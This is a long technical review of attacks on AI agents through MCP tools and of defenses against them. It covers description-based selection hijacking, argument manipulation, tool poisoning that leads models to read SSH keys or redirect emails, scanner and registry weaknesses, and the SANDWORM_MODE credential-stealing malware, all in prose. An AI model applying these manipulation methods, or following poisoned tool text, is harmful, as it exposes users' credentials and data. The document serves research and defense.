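If an altered tool differs from the original on one input in 20, 32 tests would reveal a difference about 81% of the time. ProbeID may still accept the tool, because it tolerates small deviations. In a separate test with changes of this size, 14 of 22 altered tools passed. ProbeID misses some changes however many tests it runs. One altered tool calculated a property of a matrix that the user had stored earlier, but the tests referred to matrices that nobody had stored, so the original and altered versions returned the same error.

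Side effects are even harder to detect because ProbeID compares only the servers' answers. A weather server that started copying documents after an update would still pass every test if it returned the right forecast.

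## Whether the author of a description can steer the agent's choice

A description can match its code and still mislead the model. If a weather server's author adds that it is the best weather tool available, many models will choose it more often than equally good rivals. A hostile author's wording may also change the arguments that the model passes to a tool, such as which file to open, or make the model misuse a different, trusted tool without ever calling the one described. Researchers have achieved all three effects in experiments, often in more than 80% of trials, though a few of the newest models resist the best-known attacks.

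### From a library of tools to one choice

A host with a handful of tools can give the model every description. With thousands of tools, all the descriptions together would be too long, so some agents first search the library for a few candidates. *Prompt Injection Attack to Tool Selection in LLM Agents* (Shi, Yuan and colleagues, 2025) describes this as a two-step process of retrieval and selection.

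The library is a set of tool documents, D = {d₁, …, dₙ}, which contain each tool's name and description. When the user asks for a task q, a retriever converts q and every document into vectors, using the encoders f_q and f_d. It then keeps the k documents whose vectors are most similar to the vector of the task:

$$D_k = \text{Top-}k_{\,d_j \in D}\; \mathrm{Sim}\big(f_q(q),\, f_d(d_j)\big)$$

The language model E reads the task together with these k documents and names one tool, d*:

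$$E(q, D_k) = d^*$$

If k is five and the user asks whether it will rain in New York, the retriever might pick five weather tools out of thousands, and the model then chooses one. A description gets its tool retrieved by resembling the questions users ask, and gets it chosen by making it seem suited to the task.

### Winning the selection

ToolHijacker, the attack in the same paper, uses a separate part of the description for each step. The first part, R, summarizes the tasks that the tool supposedly performs, so that it resembles users' requests. The second, S, is written to make the model choose the tool. The attacker can't see the real library, retriever or model, so they build a simulated agent and invent some requests. A language model then proposes variants of S, and the attacker keeps those that most often lead the simulated agent to choose the tool.

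The researchers tested this on seven tasks, each with 100 differently worded requests. For each task, they added one malicious tool to libraries of 199 and 9,650 ordinary tools. GPT-4o chose it in 96.4% of trials with the smaller library and 85.1% with the larger one. Across eight models and two versions of the attack, average success rates ranged from 70% to 100%.

Each part of the description had a different effect. In a test on one task, a description with only R always got through retrieval, but the model chose the tool in just 5% of trials. A description with only S got through retrieval in 65% of trials and was chosen in 63%, so the model almost always chose the tool when it was retrieved. A plain order to pick the tool succeeded in only 4.1% of trials with the smaller library, mostly because text unrelated to the request rarely gets through retrieval.

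In *Attractive Metadata Attack*, Mo, Hu and colleagues (2025) used tool metadata that gave the agent no orders. A language model wrote batches of names, descriptions and input schemas that looked entirely normal. The researchers tested them on a simulated agent and used the ones it chose most often as the starting point for the next batch.

The experiments covered ten kinds of work, including portfolio management and IT operations. Each agent held a fictional user's personal details and was instructed not to disclose them. The malicious tool had input fields for these details. When the attacker knew the type of work and the competing tools, the four models called the malicious tool in 81.4% to 95.6% of trials and gave it the personal details nearly as often. The three open-weight models still completed the user's task in at least 97% of trials, so a user would have had little reason to suspect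 anything.

The attack was less reliable without that knowledge, succeeding in 83.1% of trials with Gemma 3 but only 23.1% with GPT-4o-mini. When Mo and colleagues ran the agents through MCP, an attacker with that knowledge still succeeded in 81% to 88% of trials.

The attacker may be an ordinary company that wants agents to use its tool instead of a competitor's. Sneh, Yan and colleagues (2025) consider this case in *ToolTweak*. They offered the agent five suitable tools for each of ten tasks, such as weather forecasting and email validation, so an even split would give each tool 20% of the choices. An attacking model rewrote one tool's name and description up to ten times, based on how often the agent had chosen it.

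Optimizing the tool's description raised its share of the agent's choices from about 20% to 81.6% with DeepSeek's chat model, but only to about 34% with Llama 3.1. These figures slightly overstate the attack's effect because they use each tool's best round. Such optimization may be unnecessary, since four fixed sentences of boasts, such as claims about the tool's popularity and endorsements, worked better than the optimized text on five of the six models. With Grok 3 Mini, they gave the tool a share of 89.5%.

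Small details of a name can matter too. In one test, the agent strongly preferred one of two tools that were identical except for a final "1" or "2" in their names. Sneh and colleagues compare the effect to search engine optimization. Where tool providers charge by usage, better wording could bring in much more revenue for a product that is no better.

If the model selects a hostile author's tool, the author gains whatever the model sends in the call, such as a document to convert. If the server is local, its code can also act at launch, before the model selects a tool.

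### Hiding every other tool

The attacks above leave benign tools among the candidates. In *ToolFlood*, Jawad and Brunel (2026) try to fill all k candidate places with the attacker's tools, so that the model has no benign one to choose.

The attacker starts with a sample of likely requests. A language model writes 10,000 candidate tools, each meant to suit a group of 20 requests. Let N(q) be the number of the attacker's tools whose vectors are close to request q. With a limit on how many tools to publish, the attacker looks for the set that gives the largest value of

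$$\sum_q \min\{k,\; N(q)\}$$

If the retriever returns only five tools, the cap at k means that a sixth tool near the same request adds no benefit. A simple procedure adds one tool at a time, each time choosing the one near the most requests that still have fewer than k such tools.

The attack required adding an average of 145 tools to a library of 11,759, or about 1.2%. For new requests about the same tasks, the attacker's tools filled all five places 91% of the time, and the agents called one of them about 95% of the time. With 30 added tools, agents called one for roughly nine requests in ten. The tools in the experiment did nothing useful or harmful, so the direct damage was a failed task.

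On GPT-4o, hiding the legitimate tools added little to the attack's success. With ten malicious tools in the smaller library, ToolFlood succeeded for 77.2% of requests and Mo and colleagues' attack for 76.6%, although ToolFlood took over the whole candidate list far more often. Hiding the legitimate tools should matter more with a model that is less influenced by persuasive wording, because it removes the alternatives, but the model can still use no tool at all.

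The best of six defenses limited each publisher to two of the candidate tools. It prevented full takeovers and reduced the attack's success from 84.8% to 41.4%. But an attacker with a few accounts could get around it, and the official MCP registry requires only a free GitHub account to publish. Jawad and Brunel therefore recommend combining such limits with identities that are hard to fake.

This attack works only if the host searches a large, open catalog. A coding assistant that loads every tool from four servers listed in its configuration file, for example, has no retrieval step to flood.

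### Changing what the model asks a tool to do

An attacker may also want the model to call a tool with the wrong arguments. *Subverting Tool Arguments* (Dai, Sun and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to summarize a project report, but the description of the file-reading tool leads the model to request the user's private SSH key instead. The tool correctly opens the file named in the call, so testing its code would reveal no fault.

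Earlier attacks of this kind produced conspicuous text. One of them, Climbing the Hill, wrote descriptions with a median length of 304 tokens (words or parts of words), about 40 times that of ordinary ones. It succeeded in 81.2% of tests on a benchmark called MCP Security Bench. When the researchers limited the length of its descriptions, its success rate fell to 31%. OpenAI already rejects tool descriptions longer than 1,024 characters.

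The researchers' own attack, GRAFT, fits within such limits because its descriptions average 70 tokens. It starts with an honest description and finds the words most closely connected to the argument the attacker wants to change. A language model then rewrites the text around those words so that the attacker's value looks like part of the tool's normal documentation. The attacker tests the result on an agent and refines it.

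On MCP Security Bench, GRAFT changed the argument and got past five filters in 93.8% of tests, averaged over six models, including 2026 models such as GPT-5.6-Luna and Qwen3.8-27B. The rate was 81.5% on another benchmark and 63.8% on tasks from a third, MCPTox. The MCPTox requests already specified the argument's value, such as the exact file to open. Models were less likely to replace a value the user had stated than to fill in one the user had left open.

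The results for MCP Security Bench are multiples of one sixteenth, which suggests that this part of the study had only 16 tasks. If so, the fall from 81.2% to 31% would be from 13 successful tasks to five. Although the effect is large, this is a small sample on which to base a general length limit.

### Instructions in a tool that nobody calls

In tool poisoning, a tool's description contains instructions to the model that work against the user. The name comes from Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (1 April 2025), which demonstrated the attack on the coding assistant Cursor.

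In the first demonstration, a tool for adding two numbers had an extra text input. The tool's description told the model to read the user's MCP configuration file and private SSH key, put their contents in that input, and talk to the user about arithmetic. Cursor asked the user to approve the call, but its dialog did not show the full input, so the key was not visible.

In the second demonstration, Invariant Labs also connected a trusted email tool. The addition tool's description now stated that every email had to go to a certain address, supposedly for technical reasons. Cursor sent the user's emails there even when the user had named another recipient. The agent did not need to call the addition tool, so a log of its calls would list only the email tool.

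Trail of Bits calls it "line jumping" when a tool's description takes effect before the user can approve a call. Its demonstration used a description with a false statement that the user's operating system needed every command to begin with an extra instruction. That instruction would have let every account on the machine read and change files in the user's home folder. Claude Desktop and the other applications tested followed the description when they used other tools. MCP hosts keep their connections to different servers separate, but here the instruction passed from one server to another through the model.

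These were single demonstrations. *MCPTox* (Wang, Gao and colleagues, 2025) is a benchmark of 1,348 malicious test cases built on 45 real MCP servers with 353 tools. Each test gave the model a server's genuine tools and one poisoned tool, and then a harmless request. The attack counted as a success only if the model misused a genuine tool. Calling the poisoned tool counted as a failure because that would be easier to notice.

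To work, a malicious description had to tell the model when to act, what to do, and why the action was supposedly necessary. Older benchmarks hid malicious text in tool results. The same text worked almost 0% of the time in descriptions because it stated only what to do. *MCP-ITP* (2026) also reports this steep decline and treats tool poisoning as a separate problem.

The attacks had an average success rate of 36.5% across 20 model settings. OpenAI's o1-mini had the highest rate, at 72.8%. Models rarely refused explicitly. Claude 3.7 Sonnet did so most often, in less than 3% of cases. When an attack failed, the model had usually ignored the poisoned text or made some other mistake.

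### Whether stronger models resist better

Wang and colleagues found that more capable models were often easier to attack, and attributed this to the models' greater skill at following instructions. *When the Manual Lies* (2026) calls this a "Paradox of Capability". In its tests, the five most capable models carried out the malicious action in more than 89% of cases. A weaker model, Qwen3 32B, sometimes failed to carry it out because it couldn't manage the several steps the attack required.

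The models tested in these studies, such as GPT-4o and Claude 4 Sonnet, are now old. *WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning* (2026), which tests attacks through tools that web pages offer to agents, compares GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet with three newer models, including GPT-5.4 and Claude Opus 4.6. The average success rates of three attacks that relied on a tool's wording were lower on the newer models, falling from 74% to 59%, from 52% to 39% and from 35% to 17%. A fourth attack of this kind stayed at 36%. Two attacks that exploited the protocol still succeeded in 94% and 100% of tests.

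*MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks* (Shaikh and Montaruli, November 2026) reports the widest test on recent models, combining 18 models, 12 software frameworks for building agents, and 45 attack scenarios. Shaikh and Montaruli let the tools run and set up a server to receive stolen data, so they could see what happened. Overall, 22.9% of the attacks succeeded.

The rate depended heavily on the model. It was 0.4% for Anthropic's Claude Fable 5 and 49.7% for Amazon's Nova Pro. Only eight of 530 attacks succeeded against Claude Opus 4.8, which explicitly refused 223 times, citing the poisoned description. That refusal rate of 42% is far higher than the maximum of 3% in MCPTox, though the two tests differ.

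Claude Sonnet 5 sometimes correctly identified the text as a prompt injection but made the harmful call anyway. A host that checked only for warnings in the model's answer might therefore misclassify the attack as having failed.

These results show that more capable models aren't necessarily easier to attack. A model needs some skill to follow a complicated malicious description, but developers can also train it to distinguish such text from what the user wants. The "paradox" probably arose in models that could follow these descriptions but were still poor at making that distinction. This is an inference, because the experiments do not isolate the effect of training.

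The frameworks made little difference. Nine of them had attack success rates between 23% and 26%, and none had a deliberate defense against poisoned descriptions. Two others did better by accident, one because it rejects tools with duplicate names and the other because it limits how it runs tools. Shaikh and Montaruli sent five reports to four vendors, which rejected them all. *Weighing the Envelope* (2026) cites another study in which the software around the model explained only 0.5% of the variation in safety.

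The overall success rate mostly reflects calls to the attacker's tool, which were the evidence of success in 64.9% of the successful attacks. The researchers confirmed the theft of a secret in 12.1% of the successes, or about 2.8% of all tests.

Claude Fable 5's low rate also applies to a fixed set of attacks, based largely on published techniques. Dai and colleagues instead improved each attack with feedback from an agent and got GRAFT past the filters in 62.7% to 100% of tests on GPT-5.6-Luna, depending on the benchmark. They didn't test any Claude models, so these two studies don't show whether the most resistant models would also withstand GRAFT.

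Even less evidence exists about selection attacks on the newest models, because ToolHijacker, Attractive Metadata Attack, ToolTweak and ToolFlood mostly used models from 2024 and 2025. A model that has learned to refuse suspicious orders may still prefer a tool described as reliable and widely used, because that description contains no harmful request.

### Filters, rewriting and attackers who adapt

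A host can check tool descriptions before the model sees them. The simplest filters search for suspicious patterns, such as hidden characters or instructions to ignore the user. Shaikh and Montaruli built one from published recommendations. It rejected 20 of their 45 attack scenarios and 9 of 125 harmless descriptions.

Other filters use a language model or a trained classifier. Dai and colleagues tested five products, including scanners from Cisco and Snyk. Together, the five caught every description made from a crude template, but individual filters missed many. MCP-Shield found all the descriptions made from one kind of template and almost none from the other two, while Meta's PromptGuard 2 did nearly the opposite. An attack tuned to evade PromptGuard 2 mostly succeeded, but Snyk's scanner caught 42.7% of its descriptions on the MCPTox tasks. Running several filters together therefore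 helps against attackers who have prepared for only one.

Filtering helped little against GRAFT, even though GRAFT had no access to any filter while generating its descriptions. The five filters together caught none of these descriptions on two benchmarks and 18.7% on the third. A stricter filter, DataSentinel, flagged between 85.5% and 100% of harmless descriptions. Tool descriptions naturally contain many instructions, such as "Execute the SQL statement", so a filter that flags instructions will flag most tools.

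Some filters measure perplexity, which is how poorly a language model predicts a text, because garbled attack text has high perplexity. The more readable version of ToolHijacker got six of seven descriptions past the better of two such filters in the smaller library and all seven in the larger one. Sneh and colleagues found that their attack's descriptions had lower perplexity, on average, than the genuine ones, but they were also much longer, so a filter that uses both length and perplexity might work better.

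Another defense is to rewrite the descriptions. In the ToolTweak study, a language model paraphrased every description in neutral language before the agent chose a tool. This worked well against the fixed boasts, reducing how often Grok 3 Mini chose the promoted tool from 89.4% to 22.7%, close to a fair share. It worked less well against ToolTweak, especially when the attacker optimized the text against an agent that used the defense. The table shows how often each agent chose the promoted tool.

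| Model | No attack | ToolTweak | With paraphrasing | Attacker adapts to paraphrasing |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek Chat | 20.1% | 81.6% | 48.6% | 59.7% |
| GPT-OSS 20B | 18.9% | 73.6% | 63.3% | 67.9% |
| Grok 3 Mini | 19.9% | 50.7% | 32.7% | 44.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 18.8% | 48.6% | 30.1% | 37.5% |
| Qwen 2.5 7B | 19.9% | 45.9% | 34.3% | 46.7% |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 19.8% | 33.9% | 27.2% | 34.4% |

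With Qwen and Llama, the adapting attacker regained everything it had lost to the defense. This may be partly because the defense rewrites the description but keeps the tool's name, which also influences the agent's choice. A paraphrase can also remove praise but keep a false factual claim. TrustDesc discards the author's text and generates a description from the source code, so it works only when that code is available.

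Warnings in the agent's standing instructions had mixed results. Mo and colleagues told agents to reject tools that looked hostile or unusual. This lowered the attack success rate by less than seven percentage points on every model when the attacker knew the task. It helped more against the uninformed attacker, lowering the rate from 83.1% to 60.8% on Gemma 3. *Weighing the Envelope* cites an experiment by Singh and Mittal in which the same change to the prompt helped some models and harmed others, so a host would have to test such a defense on each model.

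Developers can also train the model to ignore instructions hidden in outside data, using methods such as StruQ and SecAlign. Shi, Yuan and colleagues found that models trained this way still chose ToolHijacker's tool in 87% to nearly 100% of trials. ToolHijacker's descriptions stay on the subject of the user's task, so they contain little that such a model would recognize as an outside instruction.

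GRAFT also worked against the filters combined with three other defenses. One repeats the user's request to the model, another runs the task a second time without that request to see whether the same call appears, and a third removes unnecessary data from tool calls. With all of them active, GRAFT succeeded in 50.7% to 81.2% of tests on Qwen3.8-27B, depending on the benchmark, while the crude templates failed every time.

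Dai and colleagues then trained the same model on examples of GRAFT's own descriptions, with the correct call as the preferred answer. On new examples, GRAFT's success rate fell from 84.4% to 37.8%, and attacks not used in the training also became much weaker. But the model's score for choosing tools when there was no attack fell too, from 93.3% to 78%. Its general knowledge was unaffected, so a developer who ran only a standard knowledge test would not have noticed the loss.

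## Whether scanners and registries can find malicious tools

A filter that reads only descriptions can't find malicious code in a tool whose description looks harmless. Scanners that read the code can, but in the main test so far, the ones that caught most malicious tools also flagged most harmless ones. Many registries list servers without examining their code.

### What each method looks for

*MalTool* (Hu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool with the description "Send email using SendGrid API." The tool does send the user's email through SendGrid, a real email delivery service, but first it sends a copy of the recipient's address, the subject and the text to an attacker's machine. Its name, inputs and description are the same as those of the harmless original, so a filter that checks only this text can't detect the attack.

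The same is true of many accidental flaws. *VIPER-MCP* (2026), which tests a scanner for such flaws, explains that the danger often comes from how the code passes a tool's input to a sensitive operation, which the description doesn't show. One of the two existing scanners in its comparison missed flaws for this reason. The other, MCPSafetyScanner, often treated ordinary abilities, such as reading files, as evidence of an attack.

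Static analysis examines code without running it. Simple versions search for risky patterns, such as obfuscated code, while more thorough ones trace data through the program, for example from a tool's input to a network request. It needs access to the code, so it can't be used on most remote servers. It also can't easily establish intent, because a backup tool and a tool that steals documents may perform the same operations.

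Antivirus scanning checks files for patterns found in known malware. VirusTotal, a Google service, checks a file with many antivirus products at once. This works well when criminals reuse a program, but malicious code newly written for one MCP tool may not resemble any known malware.

In model-based review, a language model reads the code, often together with the description. It might flag an email tool that contacts a second address for no apparent reason. However, the attacker writes the code and could include comments meant to make the model rate it as safe.

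Sandboxed execution runs the tool among fake files and passwords and records what it opens, changes or sends. This can work even if nobody can read the code, but it catches only tools that misbehave during the test. A tool that misbehaves only for certain users, for example, would look harmless.

Combining methods can reduce false alarms. The scanner in *VIPER-MCP* uses static analysis to find possible flaws, then runs the server to confirm them. It raised no false alarms on the study's harmless servers, but it missed kinds of flaws it wasn't built to find. Confirming a known kind of flaw is easier than finding hidden code that could do almost anything.

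### Thirteen kinds of malicious behavior

According to Hu and colleagues, an attack with a malicious tool succeeds if a user installs the tool, an agent selects it, and its code does something harmful. Earlier research mostly examined how attackers get a tool installed and selected, so this study focuses on the code. The malicious code in the study's tools runs when an agent calls the tools, not at launch.

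The study covers 13 behaviors, grouped by the security property they violate.

| Property | Malicious behaviors |
|---|---|
| Confidentiality | Sends the tool's inputs to an attacker; saves them in a local file for later theft; sends local files to an attacker; searches for passwords and keys; misuses the ones it finds |
| Integrity | Inserts false records into the agent's memory or knowledge base; deletes files; deletes database records; downloads a malicious program |
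| Availability | Takes over the processor; takes over the graphics processor; delays its answer; encrypts files |

Some of these are malicious only in context. In the experiments, the false record was an invented name and age, and the delay lasted at least a minute. Many legitimate tools also insert records or take a minute to finish. A scanner given only such a function has little basis for flagging it as malicious, so some of the misses reflect the test's design more than the scanner's ability.

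The researchers tested scanners on 1,300 standalone tools that performed only a malicious behavior, 100 for each behavior. They also used 5,727 trojanised tools, real tools from public marketplaces with one of the behaviors added. For a harmless comparison, they used 4,846 other real tools from 1,147 code repositories. They ran 130 of the trojanised tools by hand, and every one did both its advertised job and the hidden malicious one. The additions barely changed the length of the code, so a reviewer couldn't identify these tools by their size.

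### Misses and false alarms

Hu and colleagues tested VirusTotal, two programs that search code for risky patterns (Bandit and Semgrep), and three model-based scanners made for agent tools by Tencent, Cisco and AntGroup. They also report results for what they call the combined scanner, which raises an alarm when at least one of the six does. The table shows each scanner's average results over all behaviors and all categories of harmless repositories.

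| Scanner | Standalone malicious tools missed | Trojanised tools missed | Harmless repositories flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 100% | 99.7% | 0% |
| Bandit | 41% | 14% | 63% |
| Semgrep | 99% | 57% | 17% |
| Tencent A.I.G | 59% | 63% | 38% |
| Cisco MCP Scanner | 70% | 63% | 0.6% |
| AntGroup MCPScan | 85% | 63% | 36% |
| Combined scanner | 26% | 8% | 66% |

VirusTotal caught four of the 1,300 trojanised tools it checked, even though a tool counted as caught if a single antivirus product flagged it. A clean result from VirusTotal is therefore almost no evidence that a new MCP tool is safe.

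The combined scanner missed only 8% of the trojanised tools, but it would have flagged many of them even without the malicious code. Its false alarm rate ranged from 51% for repositories in the "other" category to 82% for those in cloud storage, which had only 17 repositories. Tencent's scanner flagged 37% of the trojanised tools and 38% of the harmless repositories, and AntGroup's flagged 37% and 36%. The comparison is rough because the study counts malicious items by tool and harmless ones by repository. Still, an alarm from either scanner seems to be very weak evidence that a tool is malicious.

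The combined scanner also had the highest overall accuracy, at 81.4%, but a program that flagged everything would have scored 86%, because the test contained 7,027 malicious tools and only 1,147 harmless repositories.

Cisco's scanner had the most useful results. It flagged only seven of the harmless repositories, yet caught 80% to 91% of the trojanised tools that sent data to an attacker, saved it for later theft or downloaded a program. It would probably catch a weather server that uploads the user's documents when the agent asks for a forecast. But it missed at least 90% of the tools that searched for passwords, inserted false records or encrypted files.

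This success may not carry over to other malicious code. *MaliciousSkillBench* (2026) tested scanners on agent skills, which are packages of instructions and code that extend what an agent can do. A Cisco scanner caught only 2.5% to 8.2% of the malicious skills and wrongly flagged about 1% or less of the harmless ones. In one of the tests, a more sensitive scanner caught 57% of the malicious skills but also flagged 49% of the harmless ones. Changing the scanners' thresholds traded misses for false alarms, and no setting worked well everywhere.

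Real attackers could also write tools that are harder to detect than those in *MalTool*. The researchers made sure their tools worked and differed from one another, but they didn't adjust them to evade the scanners. An attacker can run the free scanners before publishing a tool and keep changing the code until they no longer flag it.

### Why most alarms would be false

Malicious tools are probably rare in a real registry, which makes false alarms a bigger problem than the table suggests. Let p be the share of tools that are malicious, m the share of malicious tools that a scanner misses, and f the share of harmless tools that it flags. The share of alarms that are real is then

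$$\frac{p(1-m)}{p(1-m) + (1-p)f}$$

Suppose a registry has 10,000 tools, of which 100 are malicious, and its scanner misses 10% of the malicious ones and flags 60% of the harmless ones. These numbers are illustrative, although the last two are close to the combined scanner's results on trojanised tools. The scanner correctly flags 90 tools and wrongly flags 5,940, so the share of real alarms is

$$\frac{90}{90 + 5{,}940} \approx 0.015$$

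or about 1.5%. If checking an alarm took ten minutes, a reviewer would need about 1,000 hours to find the 90 malicious tools. If the registry had only ten malicious tools instead of 100, about one alarm in 670 would be real.

The registry could save the reviewer's time by rejecting every flagged tool. That would leave 3,970 tools, ten of them malicious, and reduce the share of malicious tools from 1% to 0.25%. But the registry would also reject 60% of its honest developers' tools, which few registries would accept.

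With the Cisco scanner's average rates for trojanised tools, the same registry would get about 37 real alarms and 59 false ones, which a reviewer could check in two days. The other 63 malicious tools would remain in the registry. A registry with few reviewers should probably still prefer this scanner to the combined one, because people will soon ignore the combined scanner's alarms, which are wrong 98% of the time.

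To check that the combined scanner's alarms on harmless tools were false, two of the researchers inspected 200 of the flagged tools and found no explicit malicious behavior. A sample this size can't rule out a few malicious tools among thousands, but it suggests that most of these alarms were false.

Hu and colleagues recommend that scanners check whether a tool's description matches its code. This could expose the email tool, because its description doesn't mention a second recipient. However, DCIChecker found mismatches in about one tool in ten, mostly from carelessness, so this check might raise around 1,000 alarms in a registry of 10,000 tools. That would be better than 6,030, and many of the alarms would at least lead to better descriptions.

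### What registries check before listing a server

Hu and colleagues used a commercial language model to produce malicious tools for one to four cents each, far less than it costs to have a person review one. Users are unlikely to catch what a registry misses. *MCP-in-SoS* (2026), a risk assessment of open-source servers, cites earlier user studies in which people often had difficulty recognizing malicious servers.

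In mid-2025, Li and Gao collected 67,057 entries from six registries. Smithery and npm store the servers' files. The other four (mcp.so, MCP Market, MCP Store and Pulse MCP) mostly list links to code on GitHub. Different entries can lead to the same code, so there are fewer separate servers than entries.

Many of the problems arose after a registry had listed a server. In the four link-based registries, 1,379 links no longer worked. For 212 of them, the developer had deleted their GitHub account, and anyone could register its old name. An attacker who did so could put a malicious server at the old address, and the registry would keep presenting it as the original. Another 304 entries pointed to accounts whose owners had renamed them, which also left the old names available. These two groups made up about 1% of the entries in the four registries. The researchers did not measure how many had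 actually been taken over.

A review at submission would not prevent any of this, since the original server may have been safe. The registry would have to check regularly that each link still led to the same owner.

On mcp.so, some developers had accidentally published their own GitHub tokens in the setup instructions for their servers. Li and Gao found nine tokens, five of which still worked in July 2025. An attacker could have used a working token to change the developer's real server. The registry never replied to the researchers' report, but when Li and Gao collected the data again, they found only one token, which had expired.

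Package names on npm offered little protection either. The researchers found 408 groups of packages whose names differed only in a part such as "-mcp" or "-mcp-server", and in 80.6% of the groups the packages had different maintainers. Many of these packages are presumably honest projects for the same service, but a user who remembers only the service's name could easily install one from the wrong maintainer.

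Li and Gao also built a program, MCPInspect, to check servers before installation. It found 833 servers with apparent security flaws in the four link-based registries, and the researchers confirmed 37 of the 41 they examined by hand. It found suspicious descriptions in only 18 servers, mostly ones that demonstrate attacks for teaching or research. This doesn't mean that malicious servers were rare, because MCPInspect checked the code for accidental flaws and the descriptions against a list of suspicious phrases and labels. The email tool's description would pass that check.

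OX Security tested 11 marketplaces by submitting a harmless server. According to OX Security's *The MCP Supply Chain Risk*, nine accepted it without review, and only GitHub's managed registry blocked it. The summary doesn't include the result for the remaining marketplace.

The result is plausible, but the company doesn't name the nine marketplaces in its announcement or summary, or say how it submitted the server, how long the entries stayed up, or whether anyone installed them. OX Security advises users to install servers only from verified sources such as GitHub's registry. Blocking one test server is weak evidence that a registry would block others, though blocking the server is a better result than accepting it.

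The official MCP registry's name check and OpenAI's review of tool definitions might both miss the email tool's hidden copy, because the publisher's identity and the description could both be genuine.

### An analysis of 10,121 servers

In *Agent Smith in Action*, Zha, Li and colleagues (2026) collected 10,121 servers with 90,200 tools from GitHub and four marketplaces between April and July 2025. They then looked for flaws an outsider could exploit, including flaws that arise only when an agent uses several tools in a row.

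The program SCAN-MCP first finds the code that handles each tool. A language model then identifies where outside data enters this code and which sensitive operations it might reach. For each pair of tools on a server, the model also assesses whether one could affect the other, for example through a shared file. Fixed rules discard implausible combinations and limit chains to four tools. Finally, the model proposes a test that should demonstrate each flaw.

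SCAN-MCP produced 27,123 reports, 31% of which involved a chain of tools. To check their accuracy, the researchers sampled 100 servers and tried the proposed tests in a sandbox. They confirmed 124 of 150 reports (83%), including 19 of the 20 about chains. When they ran only the last tool in each of those 19 chains, none of the attacks worked.

In one example, a server has one tool that runs commands but refuses dangerous ones, and another that writes files. An attacker can have the second tool write a forbidden command into a file and the first tool run the file. A reviewer who examined either tool alone might approve it. In a second example, an agent opens an attacker's website in a browser, clicks a button and uploads a private file from the user's machine. The browser server's developers first considered the report outside the scope of their security policy but fixed the problem about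 two weeks later.

The researchers ran other scanners on the same 100 servers. They confirmed 37% of the reports from Tencent's scanner and 19% of those from Semgrep. Cisco's scanner, in a mode that compares code with descriptions, made only two reports, both wrong. SCAN-MCP also missed real flaws, including 43 that Tencent's scanner found. When the researchers turned off some of SCAN-MCP's filters, it found 44 more confirmed flaws but produced 369 more reports.

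Given these results, some of the harmless tools that Semgrep and Tencent's scanner flagged in *MalTool* probably had real, accidental flaws. Those false alarms are useful to the tools' developers, even though they don't help a registry find malware.

The total of 27,123 is not a count of confirmed flaws, and Zha and colleagues warn against using it to estimate how common flaws are. The sampled servers averaged 1.5 reports each, compared with 2.7 for all servers. Servers with at least 50 tools accounted for 31% of all chain reports but none of those in the sample, so the 83% precision may not apply to them.

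The study strengthens the case for examining tools together, but it doesn't show whether doing so can find deliberately malicious ones. Zha and colleagues assume that the servers are honest and that an outside attacker exploits them. They didn't test SCAN-MCP on trojanised tools. SCAN-MCP might flag the email tool, since it looks for user data that reaches a network request. But like TrustDesc, it could miss a malicious library or a server that copies files at launch.

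## Why coding assistants are especially exposed

A malicious server that gets past a registry and its scanners can do only as much damage as the user's account allows. A developer's account usually allows a lot, because it holds keys to systems that other people depend on. Coding assistants add to the risk because they run commands, open folders of files written by strangers, and can edit the settings that determine which servers start. In 2026, attackers planted files aimed at coding assistants in a Microsoft repository, wrote malware that adds a rogue MCP server to the assistants' configuration, and left instructions for one assistant in a Downloads folder.

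### What an assistant can reach

A coding assistant that runs without a sandbox can open anything the person who started it can. What malware searches for gives a good idea of what this includes. Raj's *SANDWORM_MODE* (2026) lists the secrets that a group of malicious npm packages searched for, and CrowdStrike's *Denying the Worm* (2026) adds notes, chat messages and clipboard history. The table shows what an intruder could do with the most useful items on a typical developer's machine.

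| On the machine | What an intruder could do |
|---|---|
| Source code | Copy it, or change it before the developer publishes it |
| Shell | Run any program the developer can run |
| npm or PyPI token | Publish new versions of the developer's packages |
| GitHub token | Read private repositories and add code to them |
| SSH keys | Log in to servers |
| Cloud credentials | Use the company's databases and computers |
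| Unlocked password manager | Look up more passwords |
| Browser sessions | Use websites where the developer is already logged in |
| The assistant's own configuration | Add a server that starts with the assistant |

Many of these secrets are easy to find. For example, npm keeps its token in a settings file at a standard location. Developers also often put other keys in environment variables, which programs started from the same terminal normally receive.

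A local MCP server has the same access to a laptop whether a coding assistant or a chat application launches it, but a coding assistant also has its own shell and file tools. If a poisoned tool description tells the model to read an SSH key, the model in a coding assistant can often read it directly, while the model in a chat application needs another server that can read files.

### From one stolen token to other people's packages

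Suppose a developer who maintains a popular npm package adds a weather server to a coding assistant, and the server is malicious. Without involving the model, the server can read the developer's npm token at launch, look up which packages the developer maintains, insert its own code into each, and publish the results as small updates. Many projects install such updates automatically, so the code soon runs on other developers' machines and looks for their tokens.

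SANDWORM_MODE, the malware that Raj analyzed, contains code for this cycle, but it reaches victims through npm packages instead of an MCP server. The security firm Socket described it in February 2026. CrowdStrike counts 19 packages in the campaign. According to SecurityWeek, the packages had names that imitated popular tools, including Claude Code, and are no longer available on npm.

On a developer's machine, the malware first collects tokens, then waits two to four days before doing anything more conspicuous. On build machines, which may exist only briefly, it acts at once. It then publishes infected versions of the victim's packages, starting with the most downloaded. With a GitHub token, it can also add a malicious dependency to the victim's repositories. It also changes Git's settings so that repositories the developer later creates or clones will spread the infection.

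The malware also installs an MCP server in a hidden folder named like a developer utility, then adds it to the configuration of Claude Code, Claude Desktop, Cursor, Continue and Windsurf, next to any legitimate servers. The server's tools have ordinary names, such as `index_project` and `scan_dependencies`, according to CyberInsider. But their descriptions contain instructions for the model to read SSH keys, cloud credentials and npm tokens, pass them to the tool as "context", and not mention this to the user.

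Malware that already runs under the developer's account could read these files itself, but the attacker likely benefits from using the assistant instead. Security software is less likely to flag file access by an assistant, and the server may remain in the assistant's configuration after the developer removes the package.

But this part of the malware may be unfinished. Raj found that the server only saves the credentials to a local file, and nothing in the analyzed code collects the file or sends it anywhere. CrowdStrike describes the server as a means of sending credentials out, but gives no details that contradict Raj's closer analysis. The malware did have other ways to send out the secrets it collected without the server. SANDWORM_MODE is therefore good evidence that attackers want to use MCP servers to steal credentials, though it doesn't show that anyone lost a key through this server.

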